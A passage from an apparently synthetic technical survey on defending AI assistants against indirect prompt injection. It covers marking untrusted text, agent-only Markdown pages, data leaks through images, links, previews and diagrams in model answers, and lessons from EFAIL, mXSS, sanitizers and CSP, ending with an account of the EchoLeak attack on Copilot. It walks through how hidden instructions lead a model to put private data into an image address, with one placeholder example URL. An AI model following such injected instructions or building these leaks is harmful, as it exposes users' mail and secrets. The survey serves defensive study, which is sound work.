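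The number of tokens added by marking untrusted text depends on how it is marked. *PARSE* (2026) calls marking free, which is nearly true when it adds only a pair of marks. Google's report *Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) estimates that repeated markers roughly double the number of tokens in the untrusted text. That is manageable for a short email, but a web page may be most of what a web agent's model reads, so the total could nearly double too.

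Google's tests also suggest that repeated markers helped mainly by interrupting typical attack phrases, rather than by marking the text. The tokenizer then split the phrases differently, and the model was less likely to recognise them as commands. This agrees with Ye and colleagues' finding that a passage's style affects a model's internal state far more than its label does. It also explains why, as *PARSE* points out, marking helps against obvious commands but much less when an injection reads like the rest of the document.

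Marking did very well in early tests because the attacks were fixed in advance. *The Attacker Moves Second* (2025) tested it on AgentDojo, a standard set of agent tasks, and the benchmark's ready-made attacks succeeded as little as 1% of the time. When a search program adapted its attacks to the defence, more than 95% succeeded. Human testers found another 265 successful attacks. The adaptive program also succeeded more than 95% of the time against another common defence, repeating the user's request after the untrusted text.

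*On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) proves why marking can't give a guarantee by itself. Let f be a marking that turns each page x into a marked page f(x) and never makes two different pages the same. For any model M, there is a possible model M′ such that

M′(f(x)) = M(x)

for every page x. In other words, M′ reacts to the marked page exactly as M reacts to the unmarked one. If M leaks data after reading some page, M′ leaks it after reading the marked version. The paper also proves the converse case, in which a model that never obeys marked text makes the system secure. So the safety of marking rests on an assumption about the model, and the adaptive attacks show that the assumption failed for the models in that test.

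Marking is still worth using for an assistant that only summarizes public pages, because it adds little overhead and most injections on those pages will be crude. However, it is too weak to be the main protection for an agent that can send mail or spend money.

### Pages that only agents receive

These choices apply when the agent and the visitor start from the same page, but some websites now offer agents a separate version. In February 2026 Cloudflare, whose network serves about a fifth of the web, introduced an optional feature called Markdown for Agents. When an agent adds a line to its request to indicate that it accepts Markdown, Cloudflare fetches the ordinary HTML page from the website, converts it and sends the agent the result. Conversion reduced Cloudflare's own announcement from 16,180 tokens to 3,150. The coding agents Claude Code and OpenCode were already requesting Markdown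 this way.

Document360's *How Cloudflare Serves Markdown to AI Agents Explained* reports that the conversion to Markdown can handle tabs and collapsible sections inconsistently and lose heading levels. It also raises a security concern, because visitors never see the Markdown version and so can't notice if something is wrong with it.

The search consultant David McSweeney demonstrated how a site could exploit this, according to Search Engine Land's *Cloudflare's Markdown for Agents AI feature has SEOs on alert*. Cloudflare forwarded the agent's request for Markdown to the website, revealing that an AI was asking. The site could then return different HTML, with altered prices or hidden instructions, for Cloudflare to convert. McSweeney proposed that Cloudflare remove the line requesting Markdown before forwarding the request. The article, published the day after the launch, reports no such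 change.

Search Engine Journal distinguishes Cloudflare's approach from cloaking, which search companies object to. In cloaking, a server decides what to show based on who is asking. With Cloudflare's approach, the agent asks for a format, and the content is supposed to stay the same. This difference helps in judging an honest site's intentions, but an agent cannot tell from the Markdown alone whether the site is honest.

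John Mueller of Google asked why a model would want a page that no user sees, and why anyone who has to check that page against the HTML wouldn't just use the HTML. This is a strong objection on security grounds, but the check doesn't have to use up the tokens saved, because ordinary software can compare the two versions without a model. It is simpler still to download the HTML and convert it to Markdown locally. The model gets the same short text, and the site can't tell from the requested format that an AI is asking.

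Sites can recognise agents without any Markdown feature. *A Whole New World* (2025) lists the usual signals: the user agent, the network address and whether the software runs scripts. The security company SPLX warned that a single server rule could give ChatGPT, Perplexity or OpenAI's Atlas browser a different page from the one people see. Updating the agent can't fully fix this, because the server decides what to send.

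Stored copies make such a page harder to trace. Chen and colleagues found that OpenAI, Anthropic and xAI reuse a page fetched for one customer to answer another customer's question. After they changed a page, OpenAI's answers began to show the change after about 30 minutes, while Anthropic and xAI gave outdated answers for a day or more. A page poisoned for a few minutes could therefore reach other users long after the site has returned to normal. Developers using Anthropic's API can see when a page was retrieved and request a fresh copy, but the researchers found neither option at OpenAI or xAI.

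Before an agent acts on an important page, the application can fetch it again as an ordinary browser from a different network and compare the two versions of the text. Advertisements and regional editions will cause harmless differences, so the comparison should focus on the facts the action depends on, such as the price, the payee or the download address.

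## How images and links in an answer leak data

### What happens when an answer contains an image

Suppose one of the messages that reached the mail assistant overnight contains a hidden instruction, and the model follows it by writing an image into its answer. In Markdown, an image is an exclamation mark, a description in square brackets and an address in round brackets. This harmless example has the word HELLO where an attacker would want private data:

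`![dot](https://images.example/dot.png?note=HELLO)`

No real server can have a name ending in .example, so this address leads nowhere. With a working address, the leak would happen in four steps:

1. The model writes the reference into its answer. The address is just more text, so it can include anything from the model's context, such as a sentence from another email.
2. The chat window converts the reference into an HTML image. A sanitizer may well let it through, because an image tag contains no script.
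3. The browser requests dot.png from the server. The request includes the rest of the address, and so the word HELLO.
4. The server records the request in its log, where the attacker can read it.

Websites normally use the part of a web address after the question mark for details such as search terms. A server can ignore that part and return the same picture every time, or return nothing. Either way, it has already received the data, so the leak needs neither a click nor a visible image. Samoilenko's attack on ChatGPT used a transparent image one pixel wide. Checkmarx's *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents* reports a test of Microsoft's Copilot Chat in which no picture appeared but the request still went out. A developer testing a chat window should therefore check the browser's network log as well as the screen.

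An attentive user might notice a suspicious address in the answer, but usually too late to stop the leak. Many chat windows display an answer while the model is still writing it, and the browser can send the request as soon as the address is complete.

### Links, previews and diagrams

Other parts of an answer can carry data in an address too. They differ in what triggers the request and which computer sends it.

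| Element in the answer | What triggers the request | Which computer sends it |
|---|---|---|
| Image | Displaying the answer | The user's |
| Link | A click | The user's |
| Link in a messaging app with previews | Posting the message | Usually the messaging company's server |
| Diagram containing an image | Displaying the diagram | The user's |
| Diagram containing a link | A click | The user's |

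Vendors disagree about whether to allow ordinary links in answers. Amazon Q for Business, an assistant for company data, could produce a link that carried the chat history to an attacker. Amazon fixed this in January 2024 by removing all links from the answers, as Willison noted at the time. Google blocks external images in Gemini but allows links. When Checkmarx reported in October 2025 that the links could carry private data, Google closed the report as infeasible to fix. Removing every link would badly damage an assistant that answers from the web, because readers need its sources, but it would harm a mail assistant much less.

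A messaging app fetches a linked page to preview it, which sends the same request as a click, according to PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps*. OpenClaw, an agent that people can operate through chat messages, was exposed in its default Telegram setup. Users can turn previews off in its settings, but PromptArmor reported no change to the default. TechNadu's *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews* also lists Slack, Discord, and Microsoft Teams with Copilot Studio as affected. Slack fetches links posted by apps unless the developer turns previews off for the message, according to Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*.

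The mail assistant has this problem at the last of its eleven points. If the employee pastes an answer containing a link into a team chat, the chat company's server may fetch the address, and the assistant's CSP has no effect on that server.

Some assistants also draw diagrams written in Mermaid, a text notation. In the code editor Cursor, these diagrams could include outside images. Embrace The Red's *Cursor IDE* showed that a comment in a source file could make Cursor leak its stored memories of the user or the access keys in a configuration file. Cursor received the report on 30 June 2025 and released a fix in version 1.3 a month later. The fix was incomplete, and CVELogic's *CVE-2025-61589* lists versions up to 1.6 as still vulnerable.

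Microsoft 365 Copilot had a version of the flaw that required the user to click a link. Its diagrams could contain a fake login button whose URL contained the user's emails. Microsoft fixed this by disabling links in diagrams, according to CyberMaterial.

### The first reports

In *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*, Samoilenko described an attack in which a website added an instruction to any text that a visitor copied, and the visitor then pasted it all into ChatGPT. The attacker could receive the user's questions and any code that ChatGPT had just corrected. Passwords and access keys were much harder to get, and the attack sometimes failed because ChatGPT's answers varied. Samoilenko thought ChatGPT should not display Markdown images at all.

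Rehberger independently found the same flaw a few days later and reported it to OpenAI on 9 April 2023. Rehberger also warned OpenAI about plugins, which let ChatGPT read web pages, because a hostile page could then steal the conversation without the user pasting anything. OpenAI replied that displaying such images was a feature and that it planned no change, according to *ChatGPT Plugins*, Rehberger's account of the exchange. Microsoft and Anthropic did fix the flaws Rehberger reported to them that year.

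Similar reports about other products followed over the next year.

| Product | Private data within reach | Vendor's response and fix |
|---|---|---|
| Bing Chat | The open page and the conversation | Fixed by June 2023, apparently with a CSP that allowed images from four Bing addresses |
| Azure AI Playground | The conversation | Fixed in September 2023 by altering the image markup so that it stayed plain text |
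| Google Bard | Earlier chat data, in an assistant that could read the user's documents | Google said by November 2023 that it had fixed the flaw |
| Writer.com | The user's private documents | First denied that this was a security issue, then apparently fixed it by 18 December 2023 |
| Google NotebookLM | Private data in the user's notebook | Reported in December 2023, fixed on 18 April 2024 after the flaw became public |
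| GitHub Copilot Chat | The chat history, which could include secrets | Reported in February 2024, fixed by June by restricting images |

The company Writer argued that real customer accounts had no access to websites, although the researchers had sent it a video of the attack. GitHub replied in March 2024 that it already knew about the Copilot flaw, which let a comment in a source file start the leak.

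Accounts of GitHub's fix differ. Embrace The Red's *GitHub Copilot Chat* suggests that the chat stopped displaying Markdown images, while Willison's *GitHub Copilot Chat* describes a block on images from untrusted addresses. Vulners' *GitHub*, an undated summary of a GitHub disclosure, supports Willison's version if it concerns the same flaw. It also mentions a notice GitHub added to inform users about links.

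### OpenAI's partial fix and what followed

In December 2023 the ChatGPT website began to check each image address with an OpenAI server before loading the picture. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* describes this as a welcome but incomplete fix. The iPhone app didn't have the check, OpenAI hadn't published its rules, and enough addresses still passed the check that small amounts of data could leak slowly. Willison called the fix "a half-baked solution", because OpenAI could simply have blocked images from outside servers.

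The security company Tenable reported another way around the check in December 2024, and OpenAI had not deployed a fix when Tenable published its advisory. OpenAI tightened the check around August 2025, more than two years after the first report. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* says that ChatGPT now loads an address automatically only if OpenAI's web crawler has already found that exact address or the user typed it. An address the model has just assembled from private data would fail this test.

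Even with the rule, loading an image can reveal some information about the user. Permiso's *ChatGPhish* showed in May 2026 that when ChatGPT summarized a web page, it could still load images chosen by the page's author. The requests revealed the user's IP address, browser type and the time of the answer, but Permiso did not show that the conversation leaked. OpenAI first said it couldn't reproduce the problem, then classed a revised report as not applicable and later as a duplicate. Permiso reported no fix.

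### The same leak in newer products

Continue is an AI assistant for the code editor Visual Studio Code. In August 2025, VerSprite's *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering Fixed in Continue* reported that a comment in a code file could make Continue leak the chat history. The comment could also make it open local files first, including the `.env` file, where programmers often keep passwords. The user only had to ask Continue to analyze the infected file. Continue's developers released a fix the day after the report. The assistant now asks before it loads an outside image and restricts access to some files. VerSprite's *Another Day, Another Leak* reported that another extension, CodeGPT, had a similar flaw and that its vendor took no action.

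Dify is a platform for building chatbots that answer from a company's documents. In December 2025, veganmosfet hid text in a PDF in one such chatbot's document collection (*Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering in RAG Chatbot Frontend*). When the user asked about a certain topic, the chatbot retrieved the PDF and sent the user's name to an outside server through an image in its answer. It could have sent anything else in the chat the same way. Dify applied no content security policy (CSP) to these images by default, and veganmosfet recorded no vendor response or fix.

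Large companies have repeated the mistake too. In the Copilot Chat test mentioned above, Checkmarx leaked an access key from a developer's computer. Microsoft decided in November 2025 that this was not a vulnerability, because the attack needed several unusual user actions, didn't work reliably and triggered warnings. That month Willison noted a report of the image leak in Google's coding tool Antigravity. Google had marked the leak as intended behaviour, but it listed data theft through prompt injection among the tool's known problems and said it was working on a fix.

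PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls* demonstrates an attack on Rovo, an assistant that can read a company's Jira tickets and Confluence documents. The attack used Rovo's tool for opening web addresses, but PromptArmor warned that Rovo also displays Markdown images. Atlassian thanked PromptArmor in May 2026 and then stopped replying. Rovo was still vulnerable when PromptArmor published the findings on 5 August.

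The most recent case is ReLeak, a set of three attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot that Cato AI Labs described in December 2026. An email with hidden instructions sat unread in the inbox until the user asked Copilot an ordinary question. In one of the attacks, Copilot put data from internal emails into an image address, and the browser's request for the image reached the attacker through Bing, according to Nexo Causal's *ReLeak* (2026). Microsoft patched the three attacks on 17 September, 11 November and 15 November. The attackers were security researchers, and Cato knew of no use by criminals, as AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026) reports. The headline of Fadilpašić's *Hackers build zero-click attacks in Microsoft Copilot* (2026) nevertheless calls this a "campaign", which suggests real thefts.

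### What the basic remedies leave open

Blocking all outside images stops answers from leaking data automatically, as long as the block also covers diagrams and anything else that fetches a file. The product can still show its own charts. Rehberger suggested handling images as a separate feature instead of relying on Markdown. That would let the application choose each image's address.

Links still need their own rule, and so does any other program that displays what the agent writes. Microsoft's Copilot Cowork could email its user without asking for approval. When the user opened the message, it loaded images from outside servers. The image addresses could include links for downloading the user's OneDrive files without a login. Willison mentions no fix in a May 2026 note on this case.

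**Allowing images only from listed addresses**, as Microsoft chose to do for Bing Chat, keeps useful pictures. It fails if an outsider can receive data at a listed address. The email program Superhuman allowed images from a Google address that also hosts online forms, which can store data sent in a request. An attacker could collect the contents of dozens of emails this way until Superhuman fixed the flaw in January 2026. Salesforce's list still included an expired web domain, which researchers registered and used to receive customer data in a test; Salesforce corrected the list. EchoLeak, another attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, also went through an allowed Microsoft service, according to *The Anatomy of a Prompt Injection* (2026).

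A safe list of allowed servers has to be short, and someone has to review it regularly. Each entry should name a server where outsiders can't read logs, store data or have requests forwarded.

An **image proxy** is a server that fetches images on the user's behalf, which hides the user's IP address and browser from the attacker. But a simple proxy forwards the image's full URL, including any private data in it. CamoLeak, an attack on Copilot Chat, could leak code and access keys from private repositories through GitHub's own image proxy. GitHub responded by turning off images in Copilot Chat on 14 August 2025, according to MintMCP.

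A proxy is more useful if it refuses addresses that the model has made up. OpenAI's rule works on this principle, but an attacker can still learn something from which known address the model chooses. If the attacker has N known addresses and the model requests k of them in order, the requests can convey at most about

k × log₂ N

bits of information. With one image per answer and 1,024 known addresses, that is 10 bits, or roughly two letters. A freely written address can hold thousands of characters. Doubling the number of known addresses adds only one bit per request, so a developer gains most by limiting the number of requests. Rehberger made similar proposals, including a limit on images per answer and a block on repeated visits to the same address.

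Even a slow leak can expose personal details. In July 2026 Willison described how Ayush Paul had used choices between prepared links to get a user's name, home city and employer out of Claude. The attack used Claude's tool for opening web pages, not its display. Anthropic has since stopped the tool from following links in the pages it fetches.

**Showing the full address before a click.** ChatGPT can warn that a link is unverified and may contain information from the conversation, according to Gend's *AI agent link safety*. The user can then copy the link or open it anyway. The warning helps when the address contains readable words, but many harmless addresses are also long and full of codes, and few people will decode one before clicking. It also doesn't protect against leaks through link previews. For the mail assistant, it would be better to make a link clickable only if its exact address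 appeared in the message the employee asked about. Any link the model altered or invented would stay plain text.

### Why new products repeat the mistake

Markdown software commonly displays images by default, so a developer who adds a ready-made Markdown component to a chat window can introduce the leak without writing any code for it. The product will still seem to work normally. In veganmosfet's experience, developers often forget the CSP or configure it badly.

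Developers also tend to guard an agent's tools more carefully than its display. Continue asked for the user's permission before fetching a web page, but the version VerSprite tested loaded images without asking. *Takedown* found the same weakness in a coding agent whose diagrams could load outside images without the user's approval.

A product can also become more dangerous without any change to how it displays answers. In Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Fixes Data Exfiltration Vulnerability in Azure AI Playground*, Rehberger rated the Azure flaw as only medium severity because the playground couldn't yet retrieve outside content. If a company later connects such a chat window to a mailbox, strangers can send it instructions and have far more data to steal. Developers should therefore reassess how the product displays answers whenever they add a data source.

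Vendors' first responses have often delayed fixes. OpenAI and Google each described the behaviour as intended, and Microsoft, in its reply to Checkmarx, assumed that users would review the code they work with. These responses are partly reasonable, since the attack requires a successful injection first, but they leave unblocked the part of the attack that is easiest to block.

A company that fixes a leak in one product may not fix it in others. Microsoft protected Bing Chat against image leaks in 2023 but was still patching such leaks in Microsoft 365 Copilot in late 2026. Rehberger warned that developers at OpenAI might build new features without knowing that the address check exists. A company can reduce this risk by giving all its products a shared display component that blocks outside images unless a team gets an exception.

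## What browsers and email programs learned about untrusted HTML

Email programs have displayed HTML from strangers since the 1990s, and websites have let visitors post it for nearly as long. Their developers had to deal with tracking images, malicious scripts and stolen data long before anyone connected a language model to a mailbox. Much of what they learned applies directly to displaying a model's answers, but much less of it applies to the content the model reads.

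### Tracking images and Gmail's proxy

An email can refer to an image on the sender's server, just as a chat answer can. Marketers use such images to track readers. *Gmail deploys image proxy servers* (Word to the Wise, 2013) explains that the sender gives each recipient a different image name, so a request for that name shows who opened the message. Spammers could use the same method to confirm that an address was real. De Kloet (2009) wrote in *Now displaying images in messages from your contacts* that Gmail therefore usually displayed no outside images until the user asked for them.

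De Kloet was announcing an exception for messages from the user's contacts. A chat window can't make a similar exception for trusted senders, because every image arrives in an answer from the assistant, even if a stranger's instructions caused the model to include it.

In December 2013, Gmail began displaying images automatically. *Images Now Showing* (Rae-Grant, 2013) told users that Google's servers would fetch the images and check them for known viruses. This hid the reader's IP address from the sender. But each image kept its unique name, so a request from Google's server could still show the sender that a particular person had opened the message. Security experts raised this concern within days, according to *Gmail Image Proxy Changes Have Privacy, Security Implications* (Dissent, 2013).

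The image proxy was a reasonable compromise for ordinary email because the sender writes the image address before sending the message, so the address contains only what the sender already knows. In a chat window, the model writes the address after reading the user's mail and can include text from that mail in it, so the same kind of proxy offers far less protection.

### EFAIL

In 2018, researchers found a way to get private text into an image address in email too. Poddebniak, Dresen and colleagues, in *Efail*, attacked S/MIME and OpenPGP, the two main standards for encrypting email so that only the sender and recipients can read it. The attacker needs a copy of an encrypted email, perhaps from a hacked server, but not the key. The simpler of their two attacks worked as follows:

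1. The attacker sends the victim a new message in three parts. The first part begins an HTML image but leaves its address unfinished, the second is the stolen encrypted email, and the third completes the address.
2. The victim's email program decrypts the middle part and joins all three into one HTML page.
3. The image address now contains the decrypted email, and the program sends it to the attacker's server when it requests the image.

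Five email programs, including Apple Mail and Thunderbird, joined the parts in this way. Apple's Mac and iPhone programs also loaded images without asking, so the victim only had to open the message. The other three required further action from the user.

This attack worked because the programs put an attacker's text and a private message into the same document, not because of a flaw in the encryption. According to the researchers' EFAIL website, a later draft of the S/MIME standard included a warning that developers should treat the parts of such a message as coming from different origins.

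The second attack altered the encrypted text. S/MIME encrypts a message in blocks, and the email program recovers each block by computing

Pᵢ = D(Cᵢ) ⊕ Cᵢ₋₁,

where Pᵢ is the readable block, Cᵢ the encrypted one, D the decryption step and Cᵢ₋₁ the encrypted block before it. The symbol ⊕ means that each 1 in Cᵢ₋₁ flips the corresponding bit of D(Cᵢ). An attacker who flips a bit in Cᵢ₋₁ therefore flips the same bit of the readable text, without knowing the key. Emails start with predictable headers, so the attacker knows some of the text and can turn it into image markup. The change also garbles the preceding block, but an attacker can arrange the markup so that the email program ignores the garbled part.

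OpenPGP had a check that could detect such changes. When the check failed, several programs showed a warning but still displayed the altered message, and displaying it could send out the text. An AI application has the same flaw if it warns about a suspicious answer while already rendering it.

EFAIL reports that decrypted text could leak from 25 of 35 tested S/MIME programs and 10 of 28 tested OpenPGP programs. Many programs blocked outside content by default, but the researchers found ways around the block in most of them. Poddebniak and colleagues note that people had until then considered requests for outside content only a privacy threat, so developers may have had little reason to look for every gap. Vendors had released fixes for various programs by May 2018. Other people then published ways around the fixes in Thunderbird and Apple Mail, and the EFAIL website doesn't say whether the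 vendors fixed those too.

### The Samy worm and lists of forbidden code

On websites, the main danger was scripts, which are program code in a page. The browser lets a script do almost anything the logged-in user can do on that site. In cross-site scripting, an attacker gets a script into someone else's website, for example by posting it in a comment.

The social network MySpace let members decorate their profiles with HTML, but filtered out script tags and certain words. In October 2005 a member named Samy Kamkar wrote a script in a form that the filter didn't recognise but some browsers ran. When anyone viewed his profile, the script sent him a friend request from their account and copied itself into their profile, where it infected the next visitor. Within about a day it had spread to more than a million profiles, and MySpace took the site offline to remove it.

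MySpace's filter failed because its developers had to predict every way of writing a script that any browser would accept. Later filters that searched for suspicious patterns weren't much better. In 2010, Bates, Barth and Jackson found in *Regular Expressions Considered Harmful in Client-Side XSS Filters* that the best browser filters were either too slow or easy to get around. Some could even create a security hole in a site that had none. An allow-list is safer because it also blocks code its developers never thought of.

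### Why browsers make sanitizing difficult

To apply an allow-list, a sanitizer has to determine which tags a text contains. This is hard because browsers try to repair and display even badly broken HTML. If an author puts an ordinary block of text directly inside a table, where HTML doesn't allow it, the browser moves the block in front of the table. In *Parse Me, Baby, One More Time*, David Klein and Johns identified 47 tags with rules complicated enough to cause trouble. Browser makers can't simply drop these repairs, because many websites depend on them.

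A typical sanitizer parses the text into a tree of elements, removes everything that isn't on its allow-list and writes the tree back out as text. The browser then parses that text. If it builds a different tree from the sanitizer's, this is called a parser mismatch.

*mXSS Attacks*, a 2013 paper by Heiderich, Schwenk and colleagues, showed that a browser could change markup even after displaying it safely. Scripts on many websites read part of the page as text and then insert it again. Browsers tidied that text in the process, for example by dropping quotation marks that seemed unnecessary, and words that had been harmless inside the quotation marks could then become code. The researchers called these mutation attacks. The first clue was a user's 2006 bug report about a browser's print preview, seemingly unrelated to security.

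Nearly all webmail services were vulnerable, including Hotmail and Yahoo Mail. Opening a malicious message was usually safe, but clicking "Reply" could run its code, because the service copied the message into the reply editor. Browser makers changed some of the behaviour after Heiderich and colleagues reported it. Some sanitizer developers also released fixes, but many sanitizers were still vulnerable when the paper came out.

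An application should therefore sanitize text in its final form and not change it afterwards. In the mail assistant described earlier, the sanitizer has to run after the Markdown converter, because the converter can create tags that the sanitizer would otherwise miss. Pasting an answer into another program has the same risk as clicking "Reply", because that program interprets the markup again.

### Sanitizing inside the browser

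*DOMPurify* (Heiderich, Späth and Schwenk, 2017) describes a sanitizer that runs in the user's browser and uses the browser's own parser. Unlike a sanitizer on a server, it can check messages that arrive encrypted and content that a script creates in the page. It suits a chat window that converts Markdown to HTML in the browser.

Using the same parser helps but doesn't guarantee the same result. DOMPurify parses the text in a separate, empty document, while the browser later parses the sanitized text at a particular place in the real page. The same characters can mean different things in the two places. *mXSS in 2021*, by DOMPurify's maintainer (Heiderich, 2021), explains why mutation attacks would remain a problem.

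In 2024, Klein and Johns measured the mismatch for 11 sanitizers that run on servers. Their program wrapped a simple test script in up to 25 layers of awkward markup, producing 12 million fragments of HTML. They ran each fragment through every sanitizer. If the output still contained the script, they tested that output in Chromium, Firefox and WebKit, the engine behind Safari.

The researchers got a script past nine of the 11 sanitizers, six with their default settings and three only after allowing more tags. Those looser settings were extreme, but most of the attacks needed only one or two additional tags, which a real website might well allow.

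The sanitizers sometimes made harmless HTML dangerous. Without any sanitizer, 855,290 fragments ran the test script. Another 19,843 ran it only after a sanitizer had processed them. In one case, a sanitizer treated an encoded tag as harmless text, then decoded it when writing the output.

To compare how a sanitizer and a browser understood a fragment, the researchers listed the position of every endpoint in each tree, such as a piece of text or an image. They then calculated

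similarity = c ÷ (n₁ + n₂ − c),

where n₁ and n₂ are the numbers of positions in the two trees and c is the number that they share. If each tree has 10 positions and they share six, the similarity is 6 ÷ 14, or about 0.43. Identical trees score 1.

The two sanitizers that withstood every attack, sanitize-html and loofah, scored only about 0.4 and 0.2 for similarity to Chromium, while one that failed scored 0.94. Parsing a page as the browser does was therefore neither necessary nor sufficient for security in this test. The two successful sanitizers encoded all remaining text in their output, so the browser could not treat that text as tags even if it parsed the page's structure differently. Klein and Johns estimate that consistent encoding would have prevented all but two of the 16 flaws they list in maintained sanitizers. However, a sanitizer that parses a page incorrectly can remove harmless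 content.

Most of those 16 flaws had fixes when the paper appeared. Two other sanitizers had no active maintainers, so the researchers began contacting projects that used them, and an Adobe project switched to a different sanitizer. Fixes can also fail to reach users. DOMPurify needs a separate parser when it runs on a server, and updating DOMPurify doesn't update that parser. Projects from Mozilla and Grafana Labs were still using an old parser with a flaw its developers had already fixed. Both have since corrected this.

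Browsers also handle the same HTML differently. When the researchers inserted the fragments into an existing page, the script ran about 669,000 times each in Chromium and WebKit but only 498,000 times in Firefox, which departed from the HTML standard. Some fragments ran only in Firefox, so it was not simply safer. Mozilla had not yet fixed the difference when the paper appeared. A developer who tests a chat window in one browser therefore can't assume that the result holds in the others.

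The browser's built-in Sanitizer API avoids the second parsing. A website gives the browser a piece of HTML and the element where it belongs. The browser parses the HTML once, for that element, removes what isn't allowed and inserts the resulting tree directly. Firefox added the API in February 2026 and Chrome in March. Websites still need a library such as DOMPurify for older browsers. The API is mainly meant to stop scripts, so developers of a chat window also have to decide which images the API's settings should allow.

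### Content Security Policy in practice

Since sanitizers will sometimes fail, Klein and Johns recommend a strict CSP as a second layer. A CSP has a separate rule for each kind of content. For example, `img-src 'self'` allows images only from the website's own address.

The main evidence on how well websites use CSP is *CSP Is Dead, Long Live CSP!* by four Google researchers (Weichselbaum, Spagnuolo and colleagues, 2016). They searched Google's index of about 100 billion pages and found policies on 1,680,867 hosts. Many sites used identical policies, so only 26,011 were distinct. An attacker could bypass 94.72% of these and run a script.

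Most of the failures were obvious, since 90.63% of the policies removed the protection by allowing scripts written directly into the page or scripts from any server. About half of the stricter policies also failed, some because an attacker could misuse a server on the allow-list. For example, some servers generate a script using a function name taken from the request. If such a server is on the list, an attacker can request a harmful script from an approved address. Of the 15 domains that websites most often listed for scripts, 14 had at least one unsafe address.

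These percentages concern scripts in 2016 and don't measure how many image allow-lists fail today. But Superhuman made the same mistake with its list of image addresses. Whoever adds a server to the list is thinking of the files it normally provides, but an attacker can use anything else on it. A CSP can also name a folder on a server, but Weichselbaum and colleagues warn that developers can't rely on this to limit what the browser loads.

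They recommend replacing script allow-lists with nonces. A nonce is a random value that the website generates for each page load and attaches to its own scripts. The browser runs only scripts with the right value, which an attacker can't guess. CSP has no nonces for images, so a chat window still needs a rule limiting the addresses it can load images from, preferably to its own server.

An image rule also works only if the script rule holds. Weichselbaum and colleagues point out that an attacker who can run scripts can get around all the other restrictions. In October 2026, Willison described a script flaw of this kind in ChatGPT that let an attacker fetch private data and send it out through an image. The flaw has since been fixed.

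### Leaks without scripts

The closest precedent for the image leak comes from research on what attackers could do if browsers blocked every script. In *post-XSS landscape*, Zalewski (2011) announced a set of notes on this question. One of the simplest attacks in the notes uses an image address with no closing quotation mark, a trick EFAIL later used. The browser treats the page's own text as part of the address until it reaches a matching quotation mark, then sends all of it to the attacker's server. That text can include secret values that protect the user's account. Chrome later began to block addresses that appear to have captured markup in this way.

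Heiderich, Niemietz and colleagues (2012), in *Scriptless Attacks*, went further, using only style rules, fonts and images. They could supply a font in which certain characters had distinctive widths, then use style rules to make the layout react to those widths. The browser requested different files depending on the layout, so the requests revealed which characters were on the page. Their main example was stealing a credit card number from a shopping site without the user clicking on anything. They also wrote a patch for Firefox that prevented some of the attacks. Others were still finding new uses for style rules in 2025, as Gerste (2025) described in a talk also titled *Scriptless Attacks*.

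Heiderich and colleagues explain why so many defences missed these leaks. In cross-site scripting, the attacker must get content into the page, the browser must run it, and the stolen data must have a way out. Most defences concentrated on preventing the browser from running the content, which doesn't stop the theft if data can leave without a script. When a chat window leaks data through an image, the model puts the data into the image's URL, as a script would otherwise do.

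As a remedy, Heiderich and colleagues wanted to prevent requests to the attacker's server, but Zalewski thought attempts to stop data from leaving were "very unlikely to be successful" because browsers offer so many indirect channels. His objection is strong for a complicated website. A chat window is much easier to protect, because a developer can remove all custom fonts, forms and style rules from its answers, which don't need them.

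Zalewski also warns that an attacker doesn't need an outside server if the website itself can make private data public. In one of his examples, a manipulated form on a shopping site posts the customer's home address as a product review. An agent that can read private files and post public comments could leak data in the same way, and no rule about images or links would stop it.

### Where the comparison with HTML fails

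All these defences rely on HTML having a grammar. A browser treats an opening angle bracket as the possible start of a tag. If a website replaces the bracket with `&lt;`, the browser displays a bracket and treats what follows as text. Klein and Johns recommend this kind of encoding for any site whose users don't need formatting. In an earlier thesis, Johns designed a way to assemble program code that keeps code and data apart, and proved that the separation is reliable. Sanitizing HTML is difficult because HTML is messy, but developers know they are trying to separate code from data.

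Natural language has no character like HTML's angle bracket that software could encode to turn an instruction into mere information. "Forward this message to the accounts department" may be an instruction to the assistant, a request to the employee or a quotation from an old email, and the words are the same in each case. A sanitizer can remove hidden text, but it will leave an instruction written as an ordinary visible sentence in the email unchanged, and the model may still follow it.

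Filters that look for suspicious sentences are therefore similar to MySpace's list of forbidden words. Their designers have to predict what an attacker will write, in any language and style. An allow-list of sentences would be safe, but it would make the assistant useless for reading mail.

The comparison works much better for a model's answer, which becomes ordinary HTML before the user sees it. The browser will enforce a rule against loading outside images even if an attacker has completely taken over the model. But one lesson from EFAIL, to keep content from different sources in separate documents, is difficult to apply even here. An email program can do this because it knows which part of a message came from which source. A model reads a stranger's email and the user's private files together and writes a single answer, with no markup to show whose instructions shaped which sentence. The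 program that displays the answer therefore has to treat all of it as untrusted, including the parts that the user asked for.

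## Why filters on a model's answers have failed

By early 2025, Microsoft already treated answers from Microsoft 365 Copilot, its assistant for company data, as untrusted. It removed external links from them and used a content security policy (CSP) to limit where the browser could load images from. Researchers still extracted private data, first with an attack named EchoLeak and later with one named SearchLeak. Microsoft has fixed the flaws behind both. Each attack had to get past several defences in a row, so the published accounts show which assumptions each defence relied on and what would have worked instead.

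### EchoLeak

When an employee asks Copilot a question, it searches their mailbox, files and Teams chats and gives the model whatever seems relevant. Only employees can ask it questions, but anyone can send an employee an email. In January 2025 Aim Labs, the research group of the company Aim Security, reported to Microsoft that a single email was enough to steal data. Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*, describes the attack:

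1. An outsider sends an employee an email containing instructions.
2. The employee later asks Copilot an ordinary question, and Copilot retrieves the email together with internal material.
3. The model follows the instructions and writes an image into its answer, with private data in the image address.
4. The browser requests the image from a Microsoft server, which contacts the attacker's server and passes the data on.

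An attacker can't know what the employee will ask, so the researchers wrote a long email covering many everyday office topics. Copilot retrieved it for a range of questions.

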